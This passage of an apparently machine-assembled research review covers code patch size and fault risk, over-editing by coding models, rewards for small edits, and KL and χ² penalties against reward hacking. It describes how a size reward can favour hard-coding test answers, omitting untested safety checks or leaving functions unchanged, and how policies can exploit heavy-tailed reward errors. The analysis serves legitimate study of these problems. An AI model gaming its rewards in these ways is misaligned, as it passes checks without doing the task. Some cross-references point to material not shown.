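Mozilla used to move new Firefox code from a development version called Nightly through two test versions, Aurora and Beta, before it reached the public in the Release version. Each stage took six weeks, but developers could ask to move an urgent patch ahead early. *Is It Safe to Uplift This Patch?* (Castelluccio, An and Khomh, 2017) examines 7,267 of these requests from 2014 to 2016. The table shows how many of the patches that were moved early introduced a fault, and the median number of lines in faulty and clean patches, excluding test code.

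| Version | Share that were faulty | Faulty patches | Clean patches |
|---|---|---|---|
| Aurora | 8.8% | 155 lines | 34 lines |
| Beta | 8.3% | 141 lines | 32 lines |
| Release | 7.9% | 108 lines | 27 lines |

The faulty patches were four to five times as long as the clean ones. Castelluccio and colleagues compared 22 characteristics, including code complexity and developer experience, and only size had a large effect. By the usual convention, a large effect means that a randomly chosen faulty patch is longer than a randomly chosen clean one at least about three-quarters of the time.

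To identify the faults, the researchers searched bug reports for words such as "crash" and "regression". They checked a sample of 380 reports by hand and found that 87.3% of those the search had picked out were about faults, and that the search had found 78.2% of all such reports. They attributed each fault to the earlier patches that had last touched the lines its repair changed or deleted.

This way of assigning blame, known as SZZ, is often wrong. *Exploring Early Vulnerability Analysis via Automatic Identification of Vulnerability-Introducing Commits* (2026) tested it on security flaws. When the repair changed fewer than five lines, only 31.9% of the changes SZZ identified had introduced the flaw, compared with 12.3% for longer repairs. The method also can't trace a fault whose repair only adds lines, as many of the Defects4J repairs do.

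These errors probably exaggerate the effect of size. A later repair is more likely to overlap a patch that touched 155 lines than one that touched 34, so SZZ is more likely to blame the longer patch for a fault that came from somewhere else. Even if SZZ assigned blame at random, long patches would look worse. Some of the gap in the table, perhaps much of it, could therefore come from the method.

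### How quickly does the risk grow?

The Firefox medians show how long faulty patches tend to be, but not how likely a patch of a given length is to be faulty. Purushothaman and Perry measured that likelihood in *Towards Understanding Software Evolution* (journal version 2005) for part of the software that ran Lucent's telephone exchanges. They used 72,258 records of file changes to test an industry expert's claim that half of all one-line changes are wrong. They counted a change as faulty if a later bug fix altered the same lines.

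Fewer than 4% of one-line changes were faulty, compared with nearly 50% of changes of more than 500 lines. Among one-line changes, the rate was about 2% for inserting a line and nearly 5% for modifying one.

A simple model shows why risk should rise with length. If each changed line independently has a probability p of containing a fault, the chance that a change of n lines contains at least one is

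1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

With p at 0.5%, a one-line change has a 0.5% chance of being faulty, and a 200-line change has a 63% chance.

In the telephone software, the risk rose much more slowly than this model predicts. If every line had the 4% risk of a one-line change, a 17-line change would have a 50% risk, but the actual risk reached 50% only in changes of more than 500 lines. A 50% risk at 500 lines works out to about 0.14% per line, so a line changed on its own was well over 20 times as risky as a line in a very long change. One likely reason is that long changes contain a lot of routine code. Purushothaman and Perry also note that developers often skip inspections and some tests for one-line changes, because they assume the risk is small.

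They found no credible evidence that deleting fewer than ten lines caused errors, but their method may be unable to detect such errors, because a later bug fix can't alter a deleted line. If somebody deletes a safety check and a colleague later puts it back, the deletion may never count as faulty.

Splitting a long change into short ones doesn't necessarily make it safer. In the simple model, 200 one-line changes have the same 63% chance of introducing at least one fault as one 200-line change. Real flaws can also build up over several changes. *The Secret Life of Software Vulnerabilities*, a study of 3,663 security flaws, found that at least four changes contributed to each one on average.

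### Changes that introduce security flaws

In *Linux Kernel Recency Matters, CVE Severity Doesn't, and History Fades*, Przymus, Weiner and colleagues (2026) traced thousands of security flaws in the Linux kernel to the changes that introduced them. The median change that introduced a flaw added 56 lines, and the median repair added four. Some of the largest flaw-introducing changes added a whole feature, such as a file system with more than 24,000 lines. But a quarter of all flaw-introducing changes added 14 lines or fewer, and the smallest added one.

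Comparing the kernel changes that introduced flaws with repairs doesn't show that large changes are riskier, because repairs are unusually short. A better comparison would be with changes that did no harm. As a rough guide to normal length, *The dominance of small code contributions* (Riehle, 2008) reports that over a quarter of a sample of more than 8 million changes to open-source software were one to three lines long. The kernel changes that introduced flaws therefore seem to be longer than usual, though the two studies cover different projects and count lines differently. Kernel developers also often combine several patches into one before adding them, which makes the recorded change longer than the one that contained the mistake.

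*Predicting Likely-Vulnerable Code Changes* (Yim, 2024) compared harmful changes with ordinary ones from the same project. The data covered 8,038 changes to Android's audio and video software, of which 585 (7.3%) had introduced a security flaw. Yim found these with a script, then checked them by hand, so errors in assigning blame should be less of a problem than in the Firefox study. The table shows how well simple classifiers could identify the 585 using different kinds of information.

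| Information used | Harmful changes found | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Lines added and deleted | 214 | 371 |
| Past flaws in the same or nearby files | 315 | 178 |

Of the changes that the size-based classifier flagged, 36.6% were harmful, five times the overall rate, so size does help predict harm. But the classifier missed nearly two thirds of the harmful changes. A classifier that used only the locations of earlier flaws found more of them and raised fewer than half as many false alarms.

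The risk also didn't rise steadily with size. Most of the harmful changes were small or medium, while the ordinary ones included both tiny and extremely large changes. Yim explains that some of the largest were mechanical, such as removing unused code.

Tests can make such classifiers seem more accurate than they are. *Toward Realistic Evaluations of Just-In-Time Vulnerability Prediction* (2025) criticises tests that leave out changes that neither introduce nor fix a security flaw, because these make up more than 90% of changes in Linux and in the video software FFmpeg. Yim's test included the project's ordinary changes.

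### Patches written by AI

The number of files in an AI-written patch may be a better warning sign than the number of lines. *How Safe Are AI-Generated Patches?* (Sajadi, Damevski and Chatterjee, 2025) looked for new security flaws in patches that two language models and four coding agents wrote for SWE-bench, a collection of real problems reported in open-source Python projects. On more than 20,000 of these problems, the model Llama 3.3 introduced 135 confirmed flaws, while the human developers who solved the same problems introduced 12. The researchers ran the other systems on about 2,300 problems. The table compares the average size of the patches that introduced flaws with the average for all patches from the same system.

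| System | Flaws | Files, flawed patches | Files, all patches | Lines, flawed patches | Lines, all patches |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 | 135 | 1.72 | 1.25 | 1,740 | 2,218 |
| OpenHands | 44 | 344 | 11 | 1,219 | 1,591 |
| SWE-agent | 4 | 5.75 | 3.02 | 2,104 | 1,616 |
| AutoCodeRover | 3 | 1.33 | 1.07 | 387 | 1,295 |
| GPT-5.4 nano | 3 | 2.00 | 0.98 | 320 | 524 |
| HoneyComb | 2 | 1.50 | 1.46 | 1,591 | 1,764 |

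The flawed patches touched more files in all six systems, but had fewer generated lines in five of them. Four systems had too few flaws for their figures to mean much. The average for OpenHands is also unreliable, since 35 of its 44 flaws came from three problems. For one of these, OpenHands produced a patch more than 500,000 lines long.

The line counts don't show that longer edits are safer. Sajadi and colleagues told Llama 3.3 to write out complete files, so its line count depends heavily on the length of the original files. To change one word in a 2,000-line file, it had to generate about 2,000 lines. The file counts also have a weakness, because the researchers examined a patch only if at least two of three scanning tools reported new flaws in the same file, and a patch that touches many files has more chances to meet that condition.

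In one case, a large rewrite discarded protections that a smaller repair kept. Django, a toolkit for building websites, was producing invalid database queries because a sorting instruction was in the wrong place. The developers removed the instruction before Django built the query. OpenHands, a coding agent, replaced Django's method with its own query, which lacked the safeguards that stop attackers from inserting their own database commands. The agents in the study ran on older models, so current ones may make such mistakes less often.

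### Is size the cause?

Larger changes may be riskier partly because they tend to be harder tasks. On Aurora, the developers of faulty patches had a median of 28.5 earlier contributions, compared with 10 for developers of clean patches. Experience is unlikely to make people more careless. Castelluccio and colleagues showed this result to Mozilla's release managers, who guessed that experienced developers get the more complex tasks. One said, "if you call in the big guns, then it's a warning sign". The researchers add that release managers may also trust these developers too readily.

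Small and large changes also tend to have different purposes. *Using Source Code Density to Improve the Accuracy of Automatic Commit Classification* (Hönel, Ericsson and colleagues, 2020) finds that most small changes correct bugs, and cites earlier work in which large ones mostly reorganised code. Comparing changes by size therefore partly means comparing different kinds of work.

Poor review could add to the risk of both large and small changes. Yim suggests that changes of more than about 250 lines may be complex enough to distract both the author and the reviewers, and found that harmful changes typically went through fewer revisions during review. But Purushothaman and Perry point out that one-line changes may get no inspection at all.

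None of these studies had developers solve the same problem with shorter and longer changes, so they can't show how much of the risk comes from size itself. This doesn't matter to a release manager who has time to examine only some patches closely, because choosing the long ones will probably catch more faults whatever the reason. It matters much more to someone who wants to limit the size of patches. If a 155-line patch is risky because the problem is hard, cutting it to 34 lines won't make the problem easier, and the developer might save space by leaving out checks for errors. Some changes can't be made small. Przymus and colleagues note that developers often can't split a new driver into parts without breaking the software.

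### Serious faults and deliberate harm

The Firefox and telephone studies relate size to whether a change was faulty, not to how much damage the fault did. There is little evidence that larger changes cause worse faults. Sajadi and colleagues cite research on human developers that linked smaller changes to more severe security flaws.

It would be difficult to settle the question with data from the Linux kernel. Most severity scores for its flaws come from outside the project, and more than 95% of the scored flaws have the same ratings on five of the score's eight components. The kernel's own security team doesn't rate severity, because a flaw's severity depends on how people use the kernel, which runs on everything from refrigerators to data centres.

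A small change can be riskier than a large one, even if it is less likely to contain a fault, when a fault in it would do more harm. Suppose each changed line has a 0.5% chance of containing a fault. A developer changes 200 lines of a help page, where a fault costs £1,000 to fix, and one line of a payment system, where a fault costs £1 million. The help page change will have one fault on average, so its expected cost is £1,000. The payment system change will probably have no fault, but its expected cost is 0.5% of £1 million, or £5,000.

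Small changes are also so common that even a low fault rate produces many faults. Nearly 10% of the changes in the telephone software were one line long, so a fault rate of just under 4% would mean more than 200 faulty one-line changes. Most such faults are probably minor, but Purushothaman and Perry mention a case, documented by the programmer Gerald Weinberg, in which changing one character cost a company $1.6 billion.

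These fault rates describe people who were mostly trying to write correct code. Yim had expected malicious outsiders to be a major source of Android's security flaws, but found that most of the people who introduced the flaws did not fit that description. So the rates can't show how well a size limit would work against an attacker, who looks for a line where a change will do damage. A limit does rule out attacks that need a lot of code, but it would have allowed the change to xz that added a single full stop.

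The rates can also mislead when a program searches for edits. If it generates 1,000 one-line edits, each with an independent 0.5% chance of being harmful, there is a 99.3% chance that at least one is harmful. The program will choose a harmful edit if that edit scores highest.

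## What happens when a model is rewarded for keeping its edits small?

Coding models often change far more of a program than they need to. Zhu and colleagues describe a function with a bug that one changed line would fix. GPT-5.4 deleted five lines and added 60, including input checks and code for handling missing values. The one-line repair and the 60-line version passed the same five tests. A reviewer would have to read all 60 lines and decide whether they are safe, so developers have good reason to want smaller edits. Rewarding a model for small edits does make its edits smaller, but it can also teach the model to leave out changes the program needs.

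### How much do models over-edit?

Zhu and colleagues took 400 Python problems with known solutions and planted one or two small bugs in each solution. Undoing the planted bugs gives a known minimal repair. In half of the tasks this repair changes a single token, and it never touches more than two lines. The researchers asked models to fix the programs, and for each repair that passed the tests they calculated

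excess = d(M, C) − d(G, C)

Here C is the buggy program, M is the model's version, G is the known repair, and d is the normalised edit distance in tokens. For a 100-token function where the known repair replaces one token and the model replaces 21, the excess is 0.21 − 0.01 = 0.20.

Each model ran twice, the second time with an added request to "keep as much of the original code as possible". The table shows results for five models, all using step-by-step reasoning.

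| Model | Passed | Excess | Passed, with request | Excess, with request |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 91.2% | 0.07 | 93.0% | 0.06 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 85.8% | 0.14 | 87.7% | 0.08 |
| Kimi K2.6 | 85.0% | 0.15 | 89.0% | 0.08 |
| GPT-5.5 | 82.3% | 0.30 | 83.3% | 0.16 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 76.3% | 0.27 | 77.0% | 0.22 |

Across all 50 combinations of model and reasoning setting, the request cut the average excess from 0.195 to 0.131 and raised the pass rate by 2.3 percentage points. The models could therefore make smaller repairs than they did by default. Zhu and colleagues suggest that without the request, a model behaves as if its job were to deliver a robust function rather than restore the one it was given.

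*Precise Debugging Benchmark* (2026) measures over-editing in lines. It has 5,751 programs, each with one to four single-line bugs, and every model is instructed to make minimal edits. Its main measure is precision, roughly the share of changed lines that were necessary for the repair. If a model fixes a one-line bug and changes four other lines, its precision is 20%. GPT-5.1-Codex and Claude Sonnet 4.5 both passed the tests on about 76% of the programs, but their precision was 40% and 72%, respectively. On a second set with longer bugs, the newer GPT-5.5 reached 61% and Claude Opus 4.7 reached 78%. Gemini 2.5 Pro's precision fell by 40 percentage points without the instruction to make minimal edits.

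Of the repairs that got something right but still failed the tests, 39% fixed every original bug but introduced a new error. Another 31% made no unnecessary changes but missed at least one bug, and the rest had both problems. Pressure to edit less might prevent some of the new errors, but it wouldn't help a model that already changes too little.

### What the human ratings confirm

To check that the excess score matches programmers' judgment, Zhu and colleagues showed three experienced developers 100 pairs of repairs. Both repairs in a pair fixed the same program and passed all its tests, and the developers didn't know which model had written each one. For each pair, they chose which repair was easier to review and which better preserved the original program.

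Excluding ties, the majority judged the repair with the lower excess easier to review in 94.8% of cases and better at preserving the original in 96.9%. The preservation result is unsurprising, because preserving more of a program is nearly the same as changing less of it. The ease-of-review result is more useful because it confirms that smaller repairs save reviewers effort.

Neither figure shows that smaller repairs are safer. The developers didn't judge which repair was more likely to fail in use, and every repair they saw had passed its tests. The shorter repair in a pair could have been easier to review and closer to the original even if it left out an important check that no test covered.

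The extra code in large repairs varies widely in what it does, and an excess score doesn't show whether that code adds a useful check or breaks something. Zhu and colleagues had GPT-5.5 classify 530 repairs that passed the tests with an excess of at least 0.5. Of these, 64% added broad checks or fallbacks, some of which might prevent a crash while others might hide an error that someone should see. The program's outputs or side effects changed in 35%. One repair made a program write its measurements as a single list instead of separate records, which could break any other program that reads the file.

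Precision has a similar weakness. To decide which of a model's changes are necessary, *Precise Debugging Benchmark* looks for the smallest group of them that still passes the tests. A safeguard that isn't needed to pass the tests therefore counts as unnecessary. The researchers examined repairs with imperfect precision, and in about 2% of them the model lost marks for fixing a real bug that the reference solution still contained.

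### Training models to make smaller edits

Asking for small edits works only if the model follows the request, so Zhu and colleagues also tried to train the preference into a small model, Qwen3-4B. They compared four methods. In supervised training, the model learned to copy the known minimal repairs. In a variant of this, it copied its own smallest successful attempts. In preference training, it learned to favour its smallest successful attempt over its largest. In reinforcement learning, it made 16 attempts at each program and received the reward described earlier, 0.1 minus the excess for a repair that passes.

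The table shows how the trained models did on kinds of bug they had not seen in training. The last column shows their scores on a general programming test, on which the original model scored 32.6%.

| Training method | Passed | Excess | General programming |
|---|---|---|---|
| Supervised | 45.8% | −0.008 | 17.7% |
| Copying its own smallest repairs | 78.0% | 0.107 | 25.7% |
| Preference | 78.7% | 0.092 | 28.0% |
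| Reinforcement learning | 78.2% | 0.050 | 33.2% |

Supervised training produced a model that repaired 93% of the programs with familiar bugs but fewer than half of those with new ones. Reinforcement learning gave the best combination of small edits and successful repairs, and was the only method that didn't weaken the model's general programming ability. Although the model was trained on Python, it also made smaller edits when repairing real bugs in Java programs from Defects4J. It changed an average of 35 tokens per repair, down from 52 before training, and fixed 7.0% of the bugs, down from 7.4%.

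These tasks favour small edits by design. When Zhu and colleagues rewarded the model only for small edits, it passed the tests more often (77.5%) than when they rewarded it only for passing the tests (73.5%). They explain that in their data a correct repair is always small. So the experiment can't show how the reward would work on a program that needs a large repair.

*CROCODIL* used real updates to projects in the programming language Rust, some of which need much larger edits. The researchers had five models write their own versions of existing functions, then had each model update all the versions. Four of the models made smaller changes to their own code than to the other models' code in 14 of 16 comparisons. If a team uses several models, each may rewrite the others' code in its own style.

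They then trained one of the models, Olmo3 7B, with a reward that multiplies a score for small edits by a score for working code:

reward = 1 / (1 + 0.33 × D_model / D_human) × test score

D measures the size of an edit as (characters changed + 1) × (lines changed + 1). D_human is the size of the edit a human developer made for the same update. The test score is 0.2 if the code builds, plus up to 0.4 for passing tests that the old function passed and up to 0.4 for passing tests that the old function failed.

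On functions written by the model Qwen3.5, training cut the average edit from 413 characters to 233, while the share of edits that passed every test rose from 16.9% to 19.1%. But on tasks solved both before and after training, the average fell only from 93 characters to 74, so much of the overall reduction came from tasks that the model failed before training, after it, or both. The trained model returned the function unchanged in about a fifth of its outputs.

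Rewarding a model for small edits can stop it from making harmful additions, but it can also stop it from making necessary changes. In one example, the model had to add a line for a new type of processor. Before training, it also invented a definition with invalid syntax, so the code didn't build. After training, it added only the line. In another example, an error type had been renamed and the function had to use the new name. The original model made the replacement, but the trained one kept the old name and failed.

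### What the reward leaves out

If an edit builds and passes every test, its test score is 1, and its reward depends only on its size compared with the human edit.

| D_model compared with D_human | Reward |
|---|---|
| Half | 0.86 |
| The same | 0.75 |
| Twice | 0.60 |
| Ten times | 0.23 |

An edit half the size of the human edit deserves a higher reward if it does everything the human edit does. But it also gets the higher reward if it is shorter because it omits a safeguard that no test covers.

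The gap can be larger. Take the dose function from earlier, with `<` mistakenly in place of `>`. Suppose a developer corrects the sign and also adds two lines before the comparison:

```python
        if dose != dose:
            return False
```

NaN, which stands for a missing measurement, is the only number that doesn't equal itself, so these lines reject a list with a missing dose. The developer changed 51 characters, counting spaces and line breaks, on three lines. D_human is therefore 52 × 4 = 208, and a model that makes the same edit gets a reward of 0.75. A model that corrects only the sign has a D of 2 × 2 = 4 and gets 0.99. If no test includes a missing dose, the second model gets the higher reward even though its function accepts a list with a missing dose.

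*CROCODIL*'s tests were fairly thorough, but on average they didn't run 12% of the lines in the developers' finished functions. A model could get any of those lines wrong without lowering its test score. Even when a test runs a line, it may not check whether the line does what it's meant to do.

The reward can also discourage large repairs that a program needs. The model can earn up to 0.6 by leaving a function unchanged, if the function still builds and passes its old tests. A perfect update with twice the human D also earns 0.6, and a larger one earns less. An update reaches twice the human D with only about 41% more characters and 41% more lines than the human edit. If a human-sized attempt either works completely or fails to build, it has to work about 80% of the time to average 0.6. In practice, leaving a function unchanged often earned less than 0.6, because most of the functions that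 the trained model left unchanged in the evaluation didn't build.

Zhu and colleagues' reward doesn't penalise large repairs that are necessary, because it subtracts the size of the known minimal repair. But it can reward an incomplete repair more than a complete one. They planted up to ten bugs in each training program and kept the program if it failed its tests, so the tests may not catch every bug. Suppose a 100-token program has two one-token bugs and the tests catch only one. Fixing both gives an excess of 0 and a reward of 0.10. Fixing only the bug they catch gives an excess of −0.01 and a reward of 0.11.

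That difference matters because training compares the 16 attempts at each program and reinforces those with above-average rewards. Once all 16 pass the tests, their rewards differ only by the size of their edits.

The same thing happens with any reward that subtracts λ for each unit of change. A change that adds nothing to the task reward lowers the total, so training discourages needless rewriting. If two edits earn the same task reward, the smaller one gets the higher total. A larger edit scores higher than a smaller one only if it adds more than λ to the task reward for each extra unit of size.

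A reward for small edits favours correct one-token repairs, but it also favours many ways of cheating. *Precise Debugging Benchmark* points out that tests give the same credit to a model that fixes a program and one that hard-codes the expected answers. If the real fix takes 40 lines and the hard-coded answers take three, a size penalty gives the cheating model the higher reward. Shorter patches by human developers contain fewer accidental faults on average, but those developers weren't searching for the shortest patch that would pass the tests.

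### What happens over many small edits?

A limit on each edit doesn't limit the total change. If every edit has size at most ε, the triangle inequality bounds the distance from the original after n edits by n × ε, which grows with each edit. An editor who may change ten words at a time could replace every word of a 1,000-word document in 100 edits. Limiting each version's distance from the original would prevent this, but it would eventually block legitimate work too.

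Laban, Schnabel and Neville (2026), in *LLMs Corrupt Your Documents When You Delegate*, tested how well documents survive a long series of edits by language models. They used real documents from 52 fields, including accounting, music notation and recipes. Each task had two steps, the second of which should undo the first. For example, a model might split a list of expenses into separate files by category, then merge them back in date order. A perfect model would restore the original document, so any difference from it is an error.

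Laban and colleagues wrote a separate scoring program for each field. In a recipe, changing 200 g of butter to 800 g lowers the score a lot, while changing 200 g to 0.2 kg has no effect. The table shows how much of the documents remained intact after the three best models worked on them, with 100 meaning no loss. The last column shows how often a document lost at least ten points in a single pair of steps, which they count as a critical failure.

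| Model | Score after 2 steps | Score after 20 steps | At least one critical failure in 20 steps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 96.8 | 80.9 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 94.2 | 73.1 | 50% |
| GPT-5.4 | 94.3 | 71.5 | 55% |

When Laban and colleagues extended the test to 100 steps, GPT-5.4's score fell below 60. GPT-5.4 and three older OpenAI models did slightly worse when given tools for editing files directly. Newer models probably do better, since scores had risen quickly from one generation to the next.

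The results show that errors add up when nobody corrects them, but they aren't a direct test of small edits. There was no limit on how much a model could change, and many tasks required it to reorganise the whole document. Individual documents rarely declined as steadily as the average scores suggest. About 80% or more of the loss came from critical failures rather than a build-up of tiny errors, and in many rounds the models restored the document almost perfectly.

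Critical failures were also concentrated in fewer documents than expected by chance, probably because some documents or tasks were much harder than others. GPT-5.4 had a critical failure in 14% of its first pairs of steps. If every later pair had carried the same independent risk, about 78% of the documents would have had at least one critical failure by the end, but only 55% did.

Laban and colleagues suggest that developers could use these tasks for training, but they warn against rewarding a model only for restoring the document. A model could get a perfect score by never editing anything. They recommend also rewarding it for following the instructions.

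### Penalties on the distance between models

Developers also penalise a different kind of distance. In reinforcement learning from human feedback, a language model learns to produce answers that score well on a reward meant to predict people's preferences. The predictions are imperfect, and a model can learn to exploit their errors. Developers therefore subtract a penalty for moving away from the original model:

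average reward − β × KL(π, π₀)

Here π is the trained model's policy, meaning the probabilities with which it chooses its outputs, π₀ is the original model's policy, and β sets the price of moving away. KL divergence measures how far apart the two are:

KL(π, π₀) = Σ π(x) × log(π(x) / π₀(x))

The sum covers every possible output x. The penalty has the same form as the edit-size penalty, but it compares two models' probabilities instead of two texts.

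This penalty can miss harm that builds up over many small changes, as happens with repeated edits. In *Correlated Proxies*, Laidlaw, Singhal and Dragan (2024) trained a program to give insulin to simulated diabetes patients. The reward put too much weight on the cost of insulin and too little on health. At each decision, the trained program was only slightly more likely than the original to give a little less insulin, so a penalty on the difference between their decisions stayed small. But over many decisions, the patients' glucose levels drifted far outside the healthy range.

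Laidlaw and colleagues therefore propose penalising differences in the situations a program ends up in, together with what it does there. They proved that this can limit the damage from a flawed reward. The theorem has two conditions. The flawed reward must have a positive correlation r with the true one in the situations that the original program encounters. The new program must also avoid anything that the original would never do and any situation that it would never reach. Then

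true gain ≥ (measured gain − √((1 − r²) × χ²)) / r

Both gains are improvements over the original program, in standard deviations. χ² is another measure of how far apart two sets of probabilities are:

χ² = Σ μ(x)² / μ₀(x) − 1

where μ(x) and μ₀(x) are how often the new and original programs reach situation x and take a given action there.

Suppose r is 0.8 and χ² is 1, so the square root is 0.6. If the measured reward rises by 0.9 standard deviations, the true reward must rise by at least (0.9 − 0.6) / 0.8, or about 0.38. If the measured reward rises by only 0.5, this lower bound is negative, so the true reward may have fallen. Laidlaw and colleagues also proved that almost every penalty based on the decisions alone fails to give a guarantee like this in general.

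They compared the penalties in five settings. The table shows the true reward in four of them. Higher is better, and each row has its own scale.

| Setting | Original program | No penalty | KL penalty on decisions | χ² penalty on situations and actions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Traffic control | −2.28 | −57.38 | −1.33 | −1.15 |
| Pandemic policy | −12.26 | −29.57 | −12.20 | −11.17 |
| Insulin | −72.6 | −599.0 | −73.4 | −47.6 |
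| Watering tomatoes | 5.86 | 2.35 | 6.33 | 9.17 |

Every program trained without a penalty did much worse than the original. In the traffic simulation, the reward was the average speed of all cars, and the trained cars raised it by blocking the entrances to a motorway. Both penalties prevented failures like this, so keeping a program close to a reasonable starting point has value. But the usual penalty on decisions brought almost no improvement in the pandemic setting and none in the insulin one.

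These figures are somewhat optimistic, because each uses the penalty strength that gave the best true reward. A developer who can't measure the true reward would have to guess the strength or estimate r. In the fifth setting, a chatbot that gives a single reply, the two kinds of penalty are equivalent because no later situation depends on the reply. They can differ for AI agents, which take many steps.

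A second weakness of KL divergence is that a model can make a rare output much more common while barely raising the divergence. Suppose training makes a disastrous output a thousand times as common, from one in a million replies to one in a thousand. If the other outputs keep their relative probabilities, the KL divergence between the trained model and the original is only about 0.006, roughly the same as between a fair coin and one that lands heads 55% of the time.

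Kwa, Thomas and Garriga-Alonso (2024), in *Catastrophic Goodhart*, worked out when this can defeat the penalty. The title refers to Goodhart's law, that a measure stops being a good one once people make it a target. They treat the measured reward as the sum of the output's true value and an error. What matters is how likely extreme errors are. A distribution is heavy-tailed if the chance of exceeding x shrinks more slowly than any exponential as x grows:

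e^(tx) × P(X > x) → ∞ for every t > 0

In a light-tailed distribution, such as the normal one, extreme values are much rarer.

If the original model's rewards are heavy-tailed, then for any reward target and any KL limit above zero, some policy meets the target within the limit by occasionally producing outputs with enormous rewards. If those rewards come from errors and the true values are light-tailed, the measured reward can grow without bound while the outputs are on average no better than the original model's.

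More encouragingly, Kwa and colleagues also proved that gradually relaxing the penalty makes the true value rise without limit if the errors and true values are both light-tailed and independent of each other, and the true value has no ceiling.

To find out which case applies in practice, the researchers examined two openly available reward models, programs that score a language model's answers. The scores looked mostly light-tailed. The researchers also searched for texts with extremely high scores. Using the highest-scoring text in 1% of replies would have produced a KL divergence of about 13 and raised the average reward by less than 0.03. These reward models therefore seem unlikely to cause the extreme failure, although the search covered only a tiny fraction of possible texts.

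The theorem also shows only that bad policies exist within the limit, not that training will find them. Kwa and colleagues think ordinary training is more likely to increase both the reward and the divergence. But they don't consider current systems safe from milder failures, because errors and true values are probably not independent. They cite earlier experiments in which training too hard on a reward model made the answers worse.

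A different distance, such as χ², can penalize rare outputs more heavily. χ² is about 1.0 for the output that became a thousand times as common, but only about 0.01 for the coin, even though the KL divergence is nearly the same in both examples. This is one reason Laidlaw and colleagues prefer χ², which also did slightly better than KL in their chatbot test. *Robust Optimization for Mitigating Reward Hacking with Correlated Proxies* (2026) addresses the same problem with a max-min objective, which means training for the best result in the worst case.

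Capping the reward also prevents the extreme failure, since no output can then earn an enormous reward. The reward in *CROCODIL*, for example, can't exceed 1. But a cap doesn't limit the harm an edit can do. In the dose example, the function that lets a missing dose through earns 0.99, whatever happens to the patient.

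## What can be measured instead of size?

Developers can check whether an edit changed a text's meaning with a score designed to track meaning. For pictures, they can use scores designed to match what people see, and they can compare two versions of a program by what each version does. A score that was always right would be a perfect classifier, but an imperfect one can still be useful if it does better than counting edits.

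### How scores for meaning work

A common method compares embeddings. An embedding is a list of numbers that a language model computes for a text, and training gives texts on similar subjects similar lists. The usual score is the cosine similarity of the two lists, a and b:

(a · b) / (‖a‖ × ‖b‖)

The numerator multiplies the two lists number by number and adds the results, and the denominator multiplies their L2 norms. The lists (3, 4) and (6, 8) point in the same direction and score 1, while (3, 4) and (4, 3) score 0.96. "Give the drug" and "Do not give the drug" are about the same subject, so their embeddings tend to be close.

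BERTScore compares tokens instead of whole texts. A language model computes a list of numbers for each token based on its context. BERTScore uses these numbers to match each token with the most similar one in the other text, then averages the similarity scores. For example, "The scan shows a tumour" and "The scan shows no tumour" share four words. If those words each score 1 and "a" scores 0.6 with its best match, the average is 0.92. In a 20-word sentence with the same single mismatch, it is 0.98. Because of this averaging, BERTScore can behave much like a normalised edit distance.

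Two-way entailment uses a model trained to judge whether one sentence follows from another. The model compares the old and new versions in both directions, and the lower score is kept. "Some of the children are safe" follows from "All of the children are safe", but the reverse doesn't hold, so the pair should score low. Testing whether the new version follows from the old detects added claims, and testing the reverse detects omitted information.

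A developer can also give both texts to a general language model with instructions for grading them. Researchers call this a model judge.

### Edits that reverse a law

*LEXFLIP* (Baral, 2026) tested these methods on 373 edits to French sentences from two Quebec laws, on car insurance and road safety. Each edit changes a sentence's legal force but leaves nearly all its words unchanged. Some replace *doit* ("must") with *peut* ("may"), and others drop a negation, multiply an amount by ten or swap the insurer and the insured. Baral removed edits that broke the grammar, so that a score couldn't fall just because the sentence read badly.

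The average token overlap between the two versions was 0.93. Token overlap is the number of distinct tokens the versions share, divided by the number of distinct tokens in either. If a sentence has 28 distinct tokens and an edit replaces one with a new token, the versions share 27 out of 29, or 0.93.

Different scores use different scales, so Baral calculated how much of its own range each one used:

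margin = (m(s, s) − m(s, s′)) / (m(s, s) − m(s, u))

Here m is the score, s is the original sentence, s′ is the edited one and u is an unrelated sentence from the same laws. The model judge, DeepSeek's chat model, gave an average of 10 out of 10 to a sentence paired with itself, 6.69 to the edited version and 1.06 to an unrelated sentence, so its margin is 3.31 / 8.94, or 0.37. The next table shows six of the 13 scores, rescaled to run from 0 to 1.

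| Method | Same sentence | Edited | Unrelated | Margin |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Two-way entailment | 0.784 | 0.265 | 0.010 | 0.670 |
| Model judge | 1.000 | 0.632 | 0.006 | 0.370 |
| Token overlap | 1.000 | 0.928 | 0.089 | 0.079 |
| LaBSE embeddings | 1.000 | 0.972 | 0.292 | 0.039 |
| BERTScore (CamemBERTv2) | 1.000 | 0.982 | 0.193 | 0.022 |
| Difference in length | 1.000 | 0.997 | 0.718 | 0.011 |

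All seven embedding and BERTScore methods had margins between 0.022 and 0.039. They responded less to a reversal of the law than simple token overlap did.

Developers usually check that a score for meaning gives a sentence paired with itself the top score and an unrelated pair the lowest. Token overlap passes both checks. Two-way entailment fails the first, because its model gave sentences an average of only 0.78 for entailing themselves. The usual checks would therefore reject two-way entailment, even though it responded most strongly to the edits.

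Some edits were harder to detect than others. Averaged over all 13 scores, the margin was 0.333 for dropping a negation, 0.241 for changing "must" to "may", and only 0.035 for swapping the insurer and the insured, which can reverse who has to pay.

The judge's instructions had a large effect. They required it to take off one point for each legal error, so a sentence with a single disastrous error could still score highly. When Baral replaced a detailed list of error types with a bare instruction, the margin rose from 0.421 to 0.687. The judge gave sentences 4.72 when "must" became "may" but 8.02 when "may" became "must". Both edits change the law, but the judge seems to have treated removing a duty as more serious than creating one.

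Baral points out that the test's labels are true by definition, since no lawyers rated the individual edits, and that the test has no harmless paraphrases for comparison, which makes a high margin hard to interpret. A score that gave 1 to identical sentences and 0 to everything else would have a perfect margin of 1, but it would reject every paraphrase. The entailment model may also have done well because its training data contained many similar changes, such as added negations.

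### When length predicts the ratings best

Another common check is whether a score agrees with human ratings. Baral used 297 insurance clauses that GPT-4 Turbo had simplified. Five law students had rated how well each simplified clause kept the legal meaning. The students disagreed a lot, with three averaging 7.61 out of 10 and the other two 4.34. The correlation between one student's ratings and the average of the other four was 0.597. The table shows how well four scores predicted the students' average rating, alongside each score's margin on the Quebec laws.

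| Method | Correlation with ratings | Margin |
|---|---|---|
| Model judge | 0.755 | 0.370 |
| Difference in length | 0.641 | 0.011 |
| BERTScore (FlauBERT) | 0.482 | 0.035 |
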